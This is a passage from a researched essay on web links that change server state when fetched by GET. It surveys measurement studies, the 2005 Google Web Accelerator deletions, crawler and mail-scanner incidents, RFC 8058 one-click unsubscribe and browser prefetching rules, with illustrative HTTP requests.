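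They had 5,828 GET and POST requests in the end, of which 939 were sensitive. About 30% of the POSTs and about 5% of the GETs were sensitive. They had set aside the few requests that used other methods because those needed no judgment. Every PUT and DELETE was sensitive and every OPTIONS request was not, consistent with the standard.

The 5% is the closest figure in these studies to the chance that a GET changes something, but it shouldn't be applied to ordinary browsing. Calzavara and colleagues logged in, looked for functions that change things, and filtered out the many requests for images and scripts. A random sample of links would contain far more articles and product pages, so a smaller share would probably be unsafe.

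The 30% figure is another reason not to assume, when reading the 2026 survey, that an interchangeable POST is dangerous. Most POSTs made no important visible change, even when people were logged in and deliberately using functions that change things.

Later researchers instead asked what share of state-changing requests use GET. *A preliminary study on the adoption and effectiveness of SameSite cookies* (Compagna, Jonker and colleagues, 2021) made a new count of the requests in a copy of the Mitch data and added a smaller collection of its own. *The State of the SameSite* (Khodayari and Pellegrino, 2022) used an automated method on the top thousand sites in the Alexa ranking.

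| Where the requests came from | State-changing requests | Sent by GET |
|---|---|---|
| Mitch data, recounted by Compagna and colleagues | 924 on 51 sites, labelled by hand | 121 (13%) |
| Compagna and colleagues' own collection | 67 on 23 sites, labelled by hand | 5 (7%) |
| Khodayari and Pellegrino | 6,951 forms on 690 sites, identified by a token | 721 (10%) |

These figures are less independent than they look. Compagna and colleagues report a combined 126 GETs among 991 requests, but more than nine-tenths of those requests come from the Mitch data. They also give a figure of "around 14%" for GET, which is slightly too high because it includes some requests that used other methods but went from one site to another. Khodayari and Pellegrino cite the Mitch data as confirmation of their own result, and they too count 121 GETs in it. (If 121 is right, the share of GETs that were sensitive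 is nearer 4% than 5%.)

Some of these GETs did little harm. Compagna and colleagues found that about 30% of those in the Mitch data were logouts. Without the logouts, GET's share of the state-changing requests falls to just under 10%. The researchers judged that most of the 121 should have used POST.

Khodayari and Pellegrino's total is the largest, but they did not submit all 6,951 forms to check that each one changed something. Their script searched saved pages for forms that contained an anti-forgery token, and they assumed that submitting such a form would cause a change. A site that puts a token in every form, including its search box, would inflate the count. A program that only follows links would not send these requests, because they require submitting a form.

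### Changes that researchers confirmed

Khodayari and Pellegrino's manual tests are the best evidence that popular sites have had unsafe GETs with real consequences. They picked three GET requests from each of the 88 sites whose token-bearing forms used GET, 264 in all, and checked whether another site could forge them. Seven requests, on four sites, could be forged. The researchers then built a working exploit for each site. An attacker could delete a user's sketches on the art site Pixiv, delete articles, videos and pictures on Brilio, create or remove a user's portfolios on Investing.com, and change a user's default settings on Mailchimp.

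Token checks failed for 7 of the 264 requests, or 2.6%. A form that deletes a sketch by GET breaks the HTTP rule even if its token check works. The other 257 requests may include many violations of the rule, which the test did not count.

They also tried turning POST requests into GETs, as Golinelli and colleagues later did on a large scale. They chose one state-changing POST at random from each of 602 sites, converted it and checked whether an attacker could use the result. They report nine successes on six sites. The number of sites, 1% of the 602, is the safer figure because three of the sites contribute two requests each, which does not fit the sampling they describe. The exploits could change a user's watchlist on IMDB and modify invoices on PayPal.

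One percent is far below the 14.9% in the 2026 survey, but the two tests measured different things. Golinelli and colleagues counted a site if any of its captured requests, including searches, produced an equivalent response. Khodayari and Pellegrino tried one request per site, chose only requests that seemed to change something, and counted a success only if the forgery worked. They would not have counted a server that accepted the rewritten GET but still checked the token.

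The researchers began notifying the sites and other affected parties in February 2021, so these faults may be long gone. The results still show that large, well-staffed companies had made this mistake in functions their users cared about.

### Web APIs

Much of the traffic between programs goes through web APIs, interfaces that a site offers to software instead of people. *Validating HTTP Semantics in REST APIs With Constructed Call Sequence Scenarios* (Sahin and Arcuri, 2026) tested 36 of them against nine rules from the HTTP specifications and found 166 faults. One rule is that an item should no longer be available after a DELETE request reports success.

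None of the nine rules requires that a GET change nothing. The tests rely on GET to inspect data. To find out whether a deletion worked, the software requests the item before and after it. But Sahin and Arcuri have come across APIs that create a resource in response to a GET, though they don't say how many. So when their software shortens a sequence of requests, it keeps any GETs that come before the request under test.

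Another approach is to examine an API's published description. *RESTRuler* (Bogner, Kotstein and colleagues, 2024) presents a tool that checks such descriptions against 14 design rules, and reports the results of running it on 2,331 of them. One relevant rule requires GET to retrieve something, and another forbids using GET or POST in place of another method. A documented GET at `/notes/42/delete` would be strong evidence of an unsafe design. But the tool reads documentation and sends no requests, so it cannot catch an operation that is described as retrieval but writes to a database. It also misses some violations that it is designed to detect, finding 68% of 111 deliberately difficult examples written by API experts.

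In *REST APIs*, Rodríguez, Baez and colleagues (2016) checked more than 78 GB of HTTP traffic from Italian mobile users for compliance with design rules. Such recordings have a similar limitation, because they show which methods programs use and at which addresses, but not what each server stored afterwards.

### Why nobody has counted the links

None of these studies gives the share of live links that change something on a server when opened, and there appears to be no published figure. Their figures for rewritten POSTs, forms with tokens and hand-picked functions are proxies, and no simple correction would convert them into that share.

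A direct count would need a large random sample of links, including those that only logged-in users see, and someone to open each link and check what happened on the server. The main obstacle is now the checking rather than logging in. Compagna and colleagues used a tool that automatically logged in to 6,180 sites with passwords people had shared publicly, but only for the part of their study on cookies. For state-changing requests they went back to hand-labelled data, because finding such requests takes a person who understands what the site does, and that work does not scale to thousands of sites. Using shared accounts would also be risky, since a crawler that opened every link might delete things that belonged to someone else.

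Calzavara and colleagues studied 60 sites, few enough that they could avoid that problem by taking care on each one. They acted only through accounts they had created. Most of their requests affected nobody else, and they immediately reversed any that did, such as friend requests. Where a site allowed it, they deleted the account at the end.

Software could instead try to predict which links are dangerous and avoid opening them, as the crawler in the 2026 survey did with its list of forbidden words. The Mitch classifier gives some idea of how well prediction works. It classified requests as sensitive or not using their method, their length, the number and type of their parameters, and a list of words such as "delete". On requests not used in its training, 78% of those it marked as sensitive really were, and it missed a third of the sensitive ones. It would probably do worse on GETs alone,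 because the method was among its most useful clues.

Researchers can see much more when they run the application themselves. Calzavara and colleagues describe an earlier tool, Deemon, that monitors a PHP application from the inside as it handles requests. A similar monitor could record every database change while a crawler followed all the links on a private copy of a site. This would measure unsafe GETs only in software that researchers can install, which excludes most large commercial sites. Researchers would also have to separate view counts and log entries from deletions.

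## Google Web Accelerator and the deleted pages of 2005

On 4 May 2005 Google released a test version of Google Web Accelerator, a free Windows program that sped up browsing, in part by prefetching pages (requesting them before the user did). Two days later, in a post titled *Google Web Accelerator* on the blog of the Chicago software company 37signals, Fried (2005) warned other developers that the program could delete their users' data and had apparently deleted data belonging to some 37signals customers. The program prefetched pages with GET requests, which the HTTP standard defines as safe. Developers argued for months about who was to blame.

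### What the program did

*Google App Speeds Up Web Surfing* (BetaNews, 2005) reported that Google Web Accelerator routed a person's browsing through Google's servers. It ran on Windows XP and Windows 2000 and worked automatically with Internet Explorer and Firefox. Marissa Mayer, Google's vice president of web products, described its methods in Search Engine Watch's *New Google Software Attempts to Speed Up Your Web Browsing Experience*. Google kept copies of pages on its own servers and compressed the data it sent. The program downloaded several parts of a page at once and tried to fetch only what had changed since the last visit. It also prefetched pages the user might want next, which an algorithm chose partly from mouse movements and overall traffic to sites.

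*Google/Web Accelerator*, a tester's notes on Tao of Mac, describes the program as a proxy (software that passes requests along) running on the user's own computer. The browser sent its requests to the proxy, with extra headers about what to prefetch. The program did not handle encrypted pages (those with `https://` addresses), but it did handle unencrypted pages behind a login. BetaNews noted that Google might temporarily store cookies and passwords sent through those unencrypted pages.

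Mayer said that some Google employees had saved over an hour a month. Consuming Experience's *Google Web Accelerator (GWA)* (2005) reports a saving of 9.1 minutes after three days, less than the time the blogger had spent working out why some sites no longer accepted a login. The blogger soon uninstalled the program.

### From a login to a deletion

Suppose someone with the program installed used the note-taking site described earlier, where each note has a delete link with a confirmation box. A note could disappear like this:

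1. The user logs in over unencrypted HTTP and receives a session cookie.
2. The user opens the list of notes, which contains a link to `/notes/42/delete`.
3. The user's pointer rests on the link for a moment, and the program chooses that address to load in advance.
4. The program sends a GET for the address, with the user's cookie.
5. The server recognizes the login, deletes the note and returns the remaining list. The program stores that page in case the user clicks.

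The third step comes from tests by commenters on Fried's post. One could get the program to load an ordinary link only by hovering over it for about half a second. Another saw the browser notify the local proxy of each link the pointer crossed. Fried probably overstated the problem when he wrote that Google was "essentially clicking every link on the page", but a user could still delete several items by moving the mouse slowly down a list with a delete link in every row.

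The confirmation box did not appear, because the program requested the address without a click. Some readers had wrongly assumed that the program was answering "yes" to the box.

Ascher (2005), in *google web accelerator vs rails*, explained that people had accepted unsafe links behind a login because search spiders and caching servers were not logged in and so never exposed the flaw. But the accelerator worked inside the browser and made its requests as the logged-in user. A reader quoted in the DShield security diary *Google Web Accelerator; Snort with ClamAV; RSA SecurID WebAgent Overflow* had warned an employer that the requests came from "a session with an authorized cookie", not an anonymous spider.

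### The missing Backpack pages

37signals found the problem on 5 May, the day after the release. According to Fried, "a few people" had reported that their pages in Backpack, the company's online organizer, were "disappearing". The staff couldn't explain the reports until they looked into how the accelerator worked. They then added code to refuse its prefetches, and within a day or so also switched Backpack's links to POST.

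Commenters on Fried's post described other damage. One said the program had deleted important sales leads through a company's database administration pages. Another could not use webmail, because the accelerator requested the sign-out link as soon as they signed in. A third had seen a forum thread where nearly half the comments were marked as deleted by their authors within the past day or two, though that could have had other causes.

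Other people tried to reproduce the deletions and failed. A commenter called matthew tested the program on several applications with GET delete links, then on a test copy of phpMyAdmin, a database management tool, and lost nothing. Another, pb, insisted for days that the program fetched only links that site owners had marked for prefetching. The confusion came partly from Google's help page, where the company explained how to mark links but also promised faster browsing without any changes to sites. After several people reported seeing unmarked links prefetched, pb mostly conceded the point. He added that, according to Mayer, the program skipped addresses containing a question mark. That would explain the failed tests if the testers' delete links contained question marks and Backpack's did not.

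One commenter suggested that Backpack users were instead clicking "delete" on other people's pages, because the program sometimes showed people pages that Google had stored for someone else. Google acknowledged this caching fault, but Mayer said in *Google speed bump draws scorn* (2005), a News.com report, that people who saw another user's name were not signed in as that user and "couldn't operate as that person". If so, the fault could not explain the deletions. Prefetching remains the better explanation, though Fried did not publish server logs that would settle the matter.

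Nobody seems to have counted the losses. Fried's "a few people" is the closest thing to a figure, and it covers only one company's customers. The News.com report misdescribed the complaint as a problem with JavaScript and the browser's back button, and quoted no figures from Google. The DShield diary did not expect a widespread disaster. The surviving reports are consistent with that, but they can't rule out losses that users didn't notice or blamed on something else.

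### A header that sites could refuse

The program added a line to at least some of its prefetch requests, which sites could use to recognize them. With that line, the request for note 42 would look like this:

```
GET /notes/42/delete HTTP/1.1
Host: example.org
Cookie: SID=31d4d96e407aad42
X-moz: prefetch
```

Ralfs writes in *Exploring the usage of prefetch headers* that Firefox had marked its own prefetches with the same header since at least 2002. A site that received the header could reply with status 403, "Forbidden", before its delete code ran. Fried recommended this and linked to code for Ruby on Rails applications. In *Breaking the Web We Have*, Bicking published a three-line rule for the Apache web server that refused every request with the header.

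Other site owners blocked the internet address ranges that Google's proxy used. padawan.info's *GWA is the new net SUV* gives instructions for both methods. Blocking Google's addresses was cruder because it turned away everyone using the accelerator, including people who clicked links themselves.

Even the header method had problems. A commenter on Fried's post pointed out that under RFC 2616 a program should not repeat a request after a 403, and proposed status 412, "Precondition Failed", instead. Another worried that a user who later clicked the link would get the stored refusal. It is also unclear whether every prefetch carried the header. The Tao of Mac tester saw it only on requests for items that a site had marked for prefetching, but Fried's advice works only if the requests that did the damage carried it too.

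The header helped only as long as Google's program kept sending it, while switching the links to POST removed the cause of the problem. One commenter called the block a patch and said Backpack was "still broken", since other programs could also use a person's cookies and follow every link without sending a header that identified them.

### Who was to blame

Many developers blamed the applications. Lefkowitz (2005), in *Google Web Accelerator == Pitiless Enforcer of Web Design Patterns*, conceded that common use of GET had drifted far from the specification, but argued that when the two conflict, the common use is wrong. Shiflett (2005), in *Google Web Accelerator and PHP*, told PHP programmers that the developers who complained had only themselves to blame. In a comment on Fried's post, the programmer Bill de hÓra answered those who contrasted the specification with reality. He wrote that,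 in reality, software following the specification had broken the applications.

David Heinemeier Hansson, the creator of Rails, worked at 37signals and took the opposite view. In *Google's Accelerator in need of a recall*, he compared the program to a faulty car. A commenter replied that a recall would be cheap, because the accelerator could update itself and Google needed only to release a version that prefetched less. In the discussion under Fried's post, Heinemeier Hansson argued that pages behind a login had been safe from spiders, and that many developers had considered this a good enough reason to depart from a rule worded only as "SHOULD NOT".

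Willison had made the same argument from RFC 2119, which allows exceptions to a "SHOULD NOT", and had called hiding delete links behind a login "a perfectly acceptable compromise". After reading the replies, Willison changed position because such links were open to cross-site request forgery even without the accelerator. Willison still thought the wording allowed exceptions for developers who had thought long and hard about the matter, but said anyone who had overlooked security and accelerators had not thought hard enough.

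RFC 2119 supports that stricter reading, because under it developers should understand the full implications and weigh the case carefully before departing from a "SHOULD NOT". Many developers had never considered the question. One, named Richard, commented under Fried's post that it would not have occurred to him to read the HTTP specification, and that he had never seen its advice on GET and POST mentioned elsewhere.

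Commenters reminded Heinemeier Hansson that a similar problem had already occurred in Instiki, his wiki program. Its "Revert" links used GET, and spiders crawling its public site had followed them and rolled pages back to earlier versions. The wiki had no login to keep spiders out, so the incident supports his claim that logins had protected other applications. But it was also a warning of what would happen once that protection failed.

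Bicking (2005) made a case against Google that did not depend on the word "SHOULD". In the comments on his October post *Google at it again*, he argued that unsafe GET links were "as old as the web itself". Many were in old applications that nobody maintained, so he thought it unrealistic to expect developers to repair them all because one new program had exposed the fault.

Bicking, in *GWA and RFC 2616*, also questioned what the standard said about responsibility. It excuses a user who did not ask for a side effect, but he could not see where it excused the maker of software that sends requests on its own. The passage on safe methods tells programmers that their software represents the user and should let the user know about actions that may have unexpected significance, which seems to count against the accelerator. But the passage then makes GET the method that needs no such warning, so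 that browsers can treat POST and the others differently, and on the text alone this puts the applications at fault.

Google was still in a good position to foresee the trouble, because its own products broke the rule. A commenter on Fried's post noted that the delete icon beside each comment on Blogger, Google's blogging service, was a plain link. Another posted a Google address that would switch a visitor's search language to Pig Latin if any web page loaded it in a frame. Rene Dudfield, commenting on Bicking's October post, wrote that Google also used unsafe GET links, including in AdWords, its advertising service, and suggested prefetching those links to see how the company reacted.

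Sites that obeyed the rule also had reason to complain. A commenter on *Google Accelerator* (2005), a post on the technology news site Slashdot, described a page with links to daily, weekly, monthly and yearly reports, and to a report on all records that took several minutes to generate. The accelerator requested all of them. Gruber (2005) compared this to ordering everything on a takeout menu and deciding what to eat once it arrived.

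Commenters also suggested ways for Google to make the program safer without waiting for applications to change. One commenter on Heinemeier Hansson's post proposed that it stop prefetching after a user sent any POST request, since logging in almost always involves one, or that it never prefetch when the request would include a cookie. Either change would have prevented prefetching in most logged-in sessions, but it would also have slowed browsing on many pages where prefetching was harmless.

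### Prefetching before 2005

Mozilla's browsers already prefetched pages, but only those that a site's author had marked with a line such as `<link rel="prefetch" href="/page2.html">`. The browser would load the marked page while it was otherwise idle. A delete link was safe unless the author marked it by mistake. Bicking thought this worked fine and could not understand why Google had gone further. Google's approach had an obvious advantage, since it could also speed up sites whose authors had not marked any pages.

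The idea of prefetching was about a decade old by then. Kroeger, Long and Mogul had used records of web traffic at the computer maker Digital Equipment Corporation to estimate how much time it could save. They found that prefetching could cut waiting time by at most 57%, compared with at most 26% for caching by a local proxy, which helps explain the interest in it.

Early objections to prefetching were often about measurement and overhead. In December 1995, Behlendorf (1995) warned that widespread prefetching would ruin traffic statistics, because site operators could no longer assume that someone had seen a page they sent. Nottingham (2005), in *Prefetching (again)*, recalled that prefetching was among the biggest topics in web caching research in the late 1990s, and that a prefetching cache sold by the company CacheFlow was controversial. The industry eventually concluded that prefetching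 wasn't worth the overhead for ordinary shared caches, and CacheFlow moved into security products under the name BlueCoat. Nottingham thought prefetching made more sense when the cache's operator worked with the publisher, as the content delivery company Akamai did.

Some people had also foreseen the danger of side effects four years before Google released its accelerator. Davison (2001), in *Assertion*, argued that "prefetching with GET is not good", because existing prefetchers could cause unwanted side effects and overload servers, and suggested extending HTTP to make prefetching safe. A month after the workshop where that paper appeared, Oskoboiny (2001) advised most people against prefetching the links in their email because some sites were broken, but did not think the problem was yet widespread enough to give up on the standard's distinction between GET and POST.

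### The question-mark rule

Google stopped offering the download within days. A participant in the Slashdot discussion found a notice that the program had reached its "maximum capacity of users". A commenter on Fried's post wondered whether the real reason was the angry complaints Google was getting.

The program returned in October 2005, and the argument resumed. Tilkov (2005), in *GWA vs. RoR*, reported that Heinemeier Hansson was complaining again, and sided with de hÓra, Sam Ruby and Joe Gregorio, who had explained why he was wrong. Andrews (2005), in *Google Web Accelerator*, warned a mailing list for WordPress developers that the new version no longer identified itself in the header, so the 403 block would not work.

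Bicking first wrote that Google had made the problems worse, then conceded in the comments that this version seemed somewhat better because it did not prefetch addresses containing "?". Prodoehl (2005), in *Google Web Accelerator*, quotes another WordPress developer, Robert Deaton, who described the same rule. The rule may not have been new. A Slashdot participant had said in May that the program skipped such addresses and that Backpack lost pages because its addresses had no question marks. But one tester of the first version believed it did fetch addresses with question marks.

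RFC 2616 contains a related rule for caches, which Connolly (2004) pointed out to the W3C's Technical Architecture Group. If an address contains a "?", a cache must not treat a stored response as "fresh" (recent enough to use without checking with the site) unless the server has given an explicit expiration time. The RFC's reason is that "some applications have traditionally used GETs and HEADs with query URLs" for operations with significant side effects.

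The 1999 standard acknowledged the practice, which supports Bicking's claim that it was old. But the exception was meant to stop caches from blocking requests that people make. If a link adds a vote and a cache answers the second click from a stored copy, the site never receives the second vote. Prefetching causes almost the opposite problem, because it sends requests that nobody has made, and RFC 2616 did not tell prefetchers to avoid question marks.

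Mozilla's browsers also skipped these addresses, but any protection this gave against unsafe links was incidental. Mozilla's *Link Prefetching FAQ* explains that browsers often can't reuse such pages from their cache, so loading them early has little benefit.

To see how well it protects them, take two addresses from Shiflett (2006), in *Google Web Accelerator Debate*. Both remove a pair of socks from a shopping cart:

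```
/delete.php?item=socks
/delete/socks/abcd
```

The accelerator would skip the first address because it contains a "?". It could prefetch the second, which would remove the socks. The last part, `abcd`, stands for an anti-forgery token, which wouldn't prevent the removal because the program copies it with the rest of the address. The accelerator would also skip harmless addresses such as `/articles?page=2`, but those pages would still load at normal speed.

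The two addresses differ only in how the developer wrote them. Rails encouraged addresses without question marks. Willison had already objected to Mozilla's rule in 2002, citing the spread of rewritten addresses. The rule therefore gave the least protection to newer applications like Backpack, but it did cover Blogger's delete links, which contained question marks.

Shiflett used these examples to defend Google. Every unsafe link he had seen people cite either contained a "?", so the accelerator would skip it, or lacked a token, so another site could already exploit it. In his view, a developer had a fair complaint only about a link like the second one above, with a token and no question mark. He was right that most of the complaining developers already had a security hole. But exploiting that hole took an attacker who knew the site and could lure a logged-in user to a malicious page. With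 the accelerator installed, the user could lose data on an ordinary visit.

Google discontinued the program in October 2008. The deletions had required an unsafe link, a logged-in session and software that opened links without the user asking, so removing any one of these would have prevented them. 37signals removed the unsafe links by switching to POST. The proposal to prefetch without cookies would have removed the logged-in session, and Mozilla's opt-in system largely avoided opening links unasked. On sites that required no login, such as Instiki's public wiki, an unsafe link and a spider were enough.

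## Crawlers, mail scanners and browser prefetching since 2005

Search crawlers, mail scanners and newer browsers have all set off unsafe links since 2005. The best-documented crawler case involves MythTV, a free program that turns a home computer into a television recorder. Its users can manage recordings through a web interface, MythWeb, which in 2006 had a delete link for each one. In *Google ate my recordings*, Chubak (2006) told the MythTV mailing list about losing an entire collection. Chubak had blocked outside access to the server instead of setting a password, then opened it to the internet to show a relative a video. By the next day the recordings were gone. Judging from the server's logs, Googlebot, Google's search crawler, had followed the delete links.

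Chubak had expected MythWeb's "Are you sure?" boxes to prevent this. But like the confirmation box on the note-taking site, they depended on JavaScript, as Carl Fongheiser pointed out in a reply that Lichti (2006) quotes.

Over two years later, QuimaxW (2009), in *Mythweb...beware the googlebot*, posted a log entry from another MythWeb server that had lost all its recordings. The request was:

```
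GET /mythweb/tv/recorded?delete=yes&chanid=2491&starttime=1232571600
```

Someone on the forum suspected an impostor, since any program can call itself Googlebot. But the sender's network address resolved to a name under googlebot.com, and QuimaxW found copies of the site's pages in Google's search results. Neither server had a login, so the crawler or anyone else could have deleted the recording by requesting the deletion URL, without a session cookie or a secret value in the URL. The October 2005 version of Google Web Accelerator would have skipped that URL because it contains a question mark, but Googlebot didn't follow that rule.

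MythTV users had argued about an earlier visit from Googlebot three weeks before Chubak's message. In *visit from googlebot*, Watkins (2006) quotes Michael T. Dean's defense of the delete links. Dean had 176 recordings and did not want a page with 176 forms, and a link that sent a POST would not work in browsers without JavaScript. He thought users should keep Googlebot out, because strangers who found an open MythWeb could delete recordings on purpose anyway. In the same thread, Steenhagen (2006) suggested that each link open a confirmation page containing a single form, and that MythWeb not run unless the visitor had logged in.

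Dean was right that a MythWeb site without a login had bigger problems than Googlebot. But Watkins pointed out that even with a login, the delete links would still be vulnerable to cross-site request forgery. A year earlier, ImperialViolet (2005) had complained that developers who learned about crawlers "just retreated behind login pages" and made the same mistakes there.

MythWeb later gained a feature meant to lock the site when it detected a bot. In *No upcoming recordings just spurious Never Record?*, Goodey (2015) quotes a user, Andre Newman, whose access control had broken. Newman had not noticed because his browser had saved the password. He found a bot in his logs "posting searches and pressing buttons", and the lockdown had not triggered. If the bot really was submitting forms, switching the delete links to POST might not have stopped it either.

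The Daily WTF, a site that collects stories of programming mistakes, has a better-known story in which Googlebot deleted all the content of a government website within a week of its launch. Most sites give a program without cookies less access, but this one turned visitors away only if a cookie marked them as logged out. Googlebot sent no cookies, so it passed the check and followed a link that an employee had accidentally copied into a public page. The story includes no logs and doesn't name the agency, so the MythTV reports are better evidence that a crawler can delete content.

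### The burden of too much reading

Google now tends to describe crawling links that perform actions as a waste of server resources. Search Engine Roundtable's *Google* (2024) quotes Gary Illyes of Google, who advised site owners to keep crawlers away from "add to cart" and "add to wishlist" addresses. Owners had complained that Google was crawling too much, and these addresses were often a large part of what it requested. Illyes said that the crawling used up server resources but "doesn't cause problems otherwise". A crawler without cookies usually can't change a customer's cart, so at worst the site may create carts that nobody will use.

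The problem was still common in 2025. According to Search Engine Journal's *Google's Crawl Team Filed Bugs Against WordPress Plugins*, addresses with action parameters accounted for about 25% of all the crawl issues Google discussed. Google's staff reported one fault to the developers of WooCommerce, a shopping plugin, who fixed it quickly. Two other plugins still had open problems.

These complaints concern the HTTP standard's other condition for safe methods, that reasonable use should not place an unusual burden on the server. A program that asks for no change meets the first condition but can still fail this one. How much a request burdens the server depends partly on whether a cache can answer it.

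The Wikimedia Foundation, which runs Wikipedia, published figures on bot traffic in April 2025. In a text carried by The Signpost (2025), Wikipedia's community newspaper, it attributed rising demand largely to programs that collect images for AI models. Engadget's *Wikipedia is struggling with voracious AI bot crawlers* reports that bandwidth used for multimedia downloads had grown by 50% since January 2024. jsr6720, in *Robots all the way down*, quotes the Foundation's finding that bots accounted for at least 65% of its most resource-consuming traffic but only about 35% of page views.

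Wikimedia's slides for a 2025 IETF meeting explain the difference. The Foundation has two primary data centers and five caching centers. People tend to read the same popular articles, so the caches can answer many of their requests. Crawlers open any address they find, including unpopular pages, so more of their requests go on to a primary data center. If the two percentages count comparable things, a page view by a bot was about three and a half times as likely to be expensive as one by a person.

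The 65% is the share of the most resource-intensive traffic that comes from bots of every kind, including search crawlers, so it does not show how much of Wikipedia's traffic comes from AI companies. Still, the Foundation's engineers repeatedly had to block crawlers to keep them from causing problems for readers.

The HTTP standard gives no numerical limit for an "unusual" burden, and a crawler can't find the limit by examining its requests one at a time. Each request for an obscure article is an ordinary read. The burden doesn't depend on cookies or secret addresses; it comes from the total number of requests, including those from other crawlers that the first one has no information about.

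### Mail filters and the unsubscribe link

Mail scanners open links that crawlers don't find, because the links are in private messages. Many of these links include everything needed to authorize an action, so a scanner can trigger the action without a cookie.

By 2017, automated requests had unsubscribed people by accident often enough for the IETF to publish a standard about it, RFC 8058, *Signaling One-Click Functionality for List Email Headers* (Levine and Herkula, 2017). Bulk email can include a List-Unsubscribe header, which gives an address for leaving the mailing list. Levine and Herkula explain that anti-spam software often fetches every address in a message's headers, and that the sender has "no mechanical way" to tell such a request from a click. A scanner has good reason not to identify itself, since a malicious site could then show it a harmless page.

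Senders had responded by adding a confirmation page, the remedy Jacobs recommended for subscriptions. Levine and Herkula accept that this prevents accidental unsubscribing, but they say that people who find unsubscribing too difficult may report the mail as junk, which makes mail systems more likely to put the sender's later messages in junk folders. They add that a mail program can't complete a confirmation page for a user who has pressed its own "unsubscribe" button, unless it interprets a page designed for people.

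Their solution uses the method to separate a scanner's visit from a decision. The sender adds a second header, List-Unsubscribe-Post, to show that it supports one-click unsubscribing. When the user asks to leave the list, the mail program or mail service sends a request like this:

```
POST /unsubscribe/k7Qx92 HTTP/1.1
Host: example.org
Content-Type: application/x-www-form-urlencoded

List-Unsubscribe=One-Click
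```

A scanner that sends a GET to the same address receives the confirmation page, and the user stays subscribed. A POST unsubscribes the user at once. The software that sends the POST must have the user's consent, but the RFC does not specify how to get it.

The request must not include cookies, so the address has to identify both the recipient and the list. Levine and Herkula recommend including a hard-to-forge value in the address, since anyone who could guess it could unsubscribe somebody else. The sender must also sign both headers so the receiving system can check them. The server must not answer the POST with a redirect, because browsers have often turned redirected POSTs into GETs. A GET would bring up the confirmation page and leave the person on the list.

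RFC 8058 does not change how senders may use List-Unsubscribe outside one-click unsubscribing, and it can't stop scanners from opening other links. Levine and Herkula note that a spammer can make spam filters send unwanted GET requests to a server just by putting the server's address in a message.

### One-time links that scanners use first

Users notice immediately when a single-use login link fails. In *Passwordless email link opened twice for some users*, a customer of Auth0, which provides login services, posted three log entries on the company's forum. The first recorded that Auth0 had sent a link. The second recorded a successful login by Apache-HttpClient, software that other programs use to send web requests. The third recorded a failed login by Safari on a Mac, presumably by the person who had asked for the link. The customer had seen this only with some people's work email and guessed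 that antivirus software was responsible.

The program needed no existing session cookie, because the secret value in the address was enough to log in. The scanner cannot be identified from the log, but the log shows that an automated request succeeded before the person's attempt failed.

Auth0's *Safelinks process* and Supabase's *Email Templates* describe the same fault with email verification links. Supabase, which provides databases and login systems, gives Microsoft's Safe Links as an example of such a scanner. According to Microsoft, a built-in policy applies Safe Links to every recipient not covered by another policy, so a site with business customers should expect to encounter it.

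Auth0 changed its default behavior in July 2022, but the reports continued. In *Safelink process with Microsoft outlook*, Maksym described account-unblocking links that had stopped working before anyone opened them. Maksym's company solved the problem for itself by adding an exception to Safe Links, but the exception doesn't help the site's other customers.

The Plugin People's *Security Scanners consuming one time links* describes approval links that show the user a warning even though the approval has gone through. In its account, the scanner opens the address after the user clicks, then sends the user's browser there. The scanner's request records the approval, so the link has already been used when the browser requests it. Because the user meant to approve, the warning is only confusing. If a scanner opened the link before anyone clicked, it could approve something that nobody had agreed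 to.

Developers have several ways to protect one-time links:

- **A typed code.** Supabase suggests emailing a six-digit code that the person enters on the site. Opening a link then can't complete the login, but the person has to copy the code.
- **A page with a button.** Supabase also suggests that the emailed link open a page where the person presses a button. In its example, the button holds the real confirmation link, which is also in the emailed address as a parameter. A scanner that goes on to open links in the page could therefore still use it up. A button that sends a POST would be safer.
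- **A separate reply to HEAD.** NextAuth.js, a login library, tells developers how to answer a scanner's HEAD request without using up the link. This helps only with scanners that send HEAD and then leave the link alone.

The second method depends on scanners not pressing buttons. berthub.eu's *Shifting Cyber Norms* argues that sites had come to accept GET requests from mail scanners, and that developers whose links broke perhaps "had it coming". But its subtitle, "Microsoft security POST-ing to you", refers to scanning that also sends POST requests. If a scanner submits the form on a confirmation page, this method no longer distinguishes it from a person. One-click unsubscribing is a little better protected, because a server can ignore any POST without the exact text that RFC 8058 requires.

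### Link previews

Many chat programs show a title and picture when someone pastes a link. To make this preview, the program or the chat company's server requests the page, often before any recipient has clicked the link. The company's server normally has no cookies for the user's account on the linked site, so if someone pastes `/notes/42/delete` into a chat, the server gets the login page and the note isn't deleted. A one-time login link could stop working, though, because it works without cookies and the server's request can use it up.

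That danger follows from how previews work, but the complaints in *"Link protect" software breaks passwordless auth*, another thread on Auth0's forum, are about email. One participant blamed either Outlook's link preview or its rewriting of addresses for using up login links, and said the same people could log in through personal Gmail accounts. Another traced many of the requests to Microsoft's network. Some users then asked for several more links and found their accounts blocked. It isn't clear from the thread whether previews or security scans were responsible, but the site would have the same problem either way.

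### How browsers prefetch now

Browser makers have more control than mail companies over what happens when their software opens a page early, and they no longer rely on GET alone to guarantee that a request changes nothing. With some exceptions, browsers now prefetch links on a page only if the site asks them to, they label each request, and they withhold the user's cookies if the link leads to another site. *Speculation Rules changed my mind about prefetching*, from dri.es, explains that browsers do not prefetch arbitrary links because prefetching `/logout` would sign the visitor out.

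A site can still ask with the `<link rel="prefetch">` hint that Mozilla's browsers supported before 2005. A newer interface, Speculation Rules, can cover a whole group of links at once:

```
<script type="speculationrules">
{"prefetch": [{
  "where": {"href_matches": "/*"},
  "eagerness": "moderate"
}]}
</script>
```

This rule is a request for the browser to prefetch any link on the page that leads to the same site, once the user seems likely to click it. The WHATWG, the group that maintains the HTML standard, defines four levels of eagerness. At "immediate", the browser should usually load the page as soon as is practical. At "eager", a momentary hover can be enough. At "moderate", the browser waits for a clearer sign, such as a pointer that stays on the link for some time, and at "conservative", it waits until the user has started to click or otherwise interact with the link. The browser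 may ignore any of these requests, for instance to save battery power.

A "moderate" rule is close to what testers saw Google Web Accelerator do in 2005, except that the site's developer now opts in.

Prefetching downloads only the page itself, but the rules can also request prerendering, in which the browser loads the page in an invisible tab and runs its JavaScript. MDN's *Speculation Rules API* warns that prerendering is riskier, because the page's scripts may record a visit or an ad view before anyone has seen the page. It also notes that some widely used browsers don't support the interface.

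Chrome may prerender a page even if the site has not opted in. According to Chrome for Developers' *Prerender pages in Chrome for instant page navigations*, this can happen when someone types an address that Chrome predicts they will visit, or holds the pointer over a bookmark. If a bookmarked link performs an action, holding the pointer over it could therefore trigger that action without a click.

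### Labels and missing cookies

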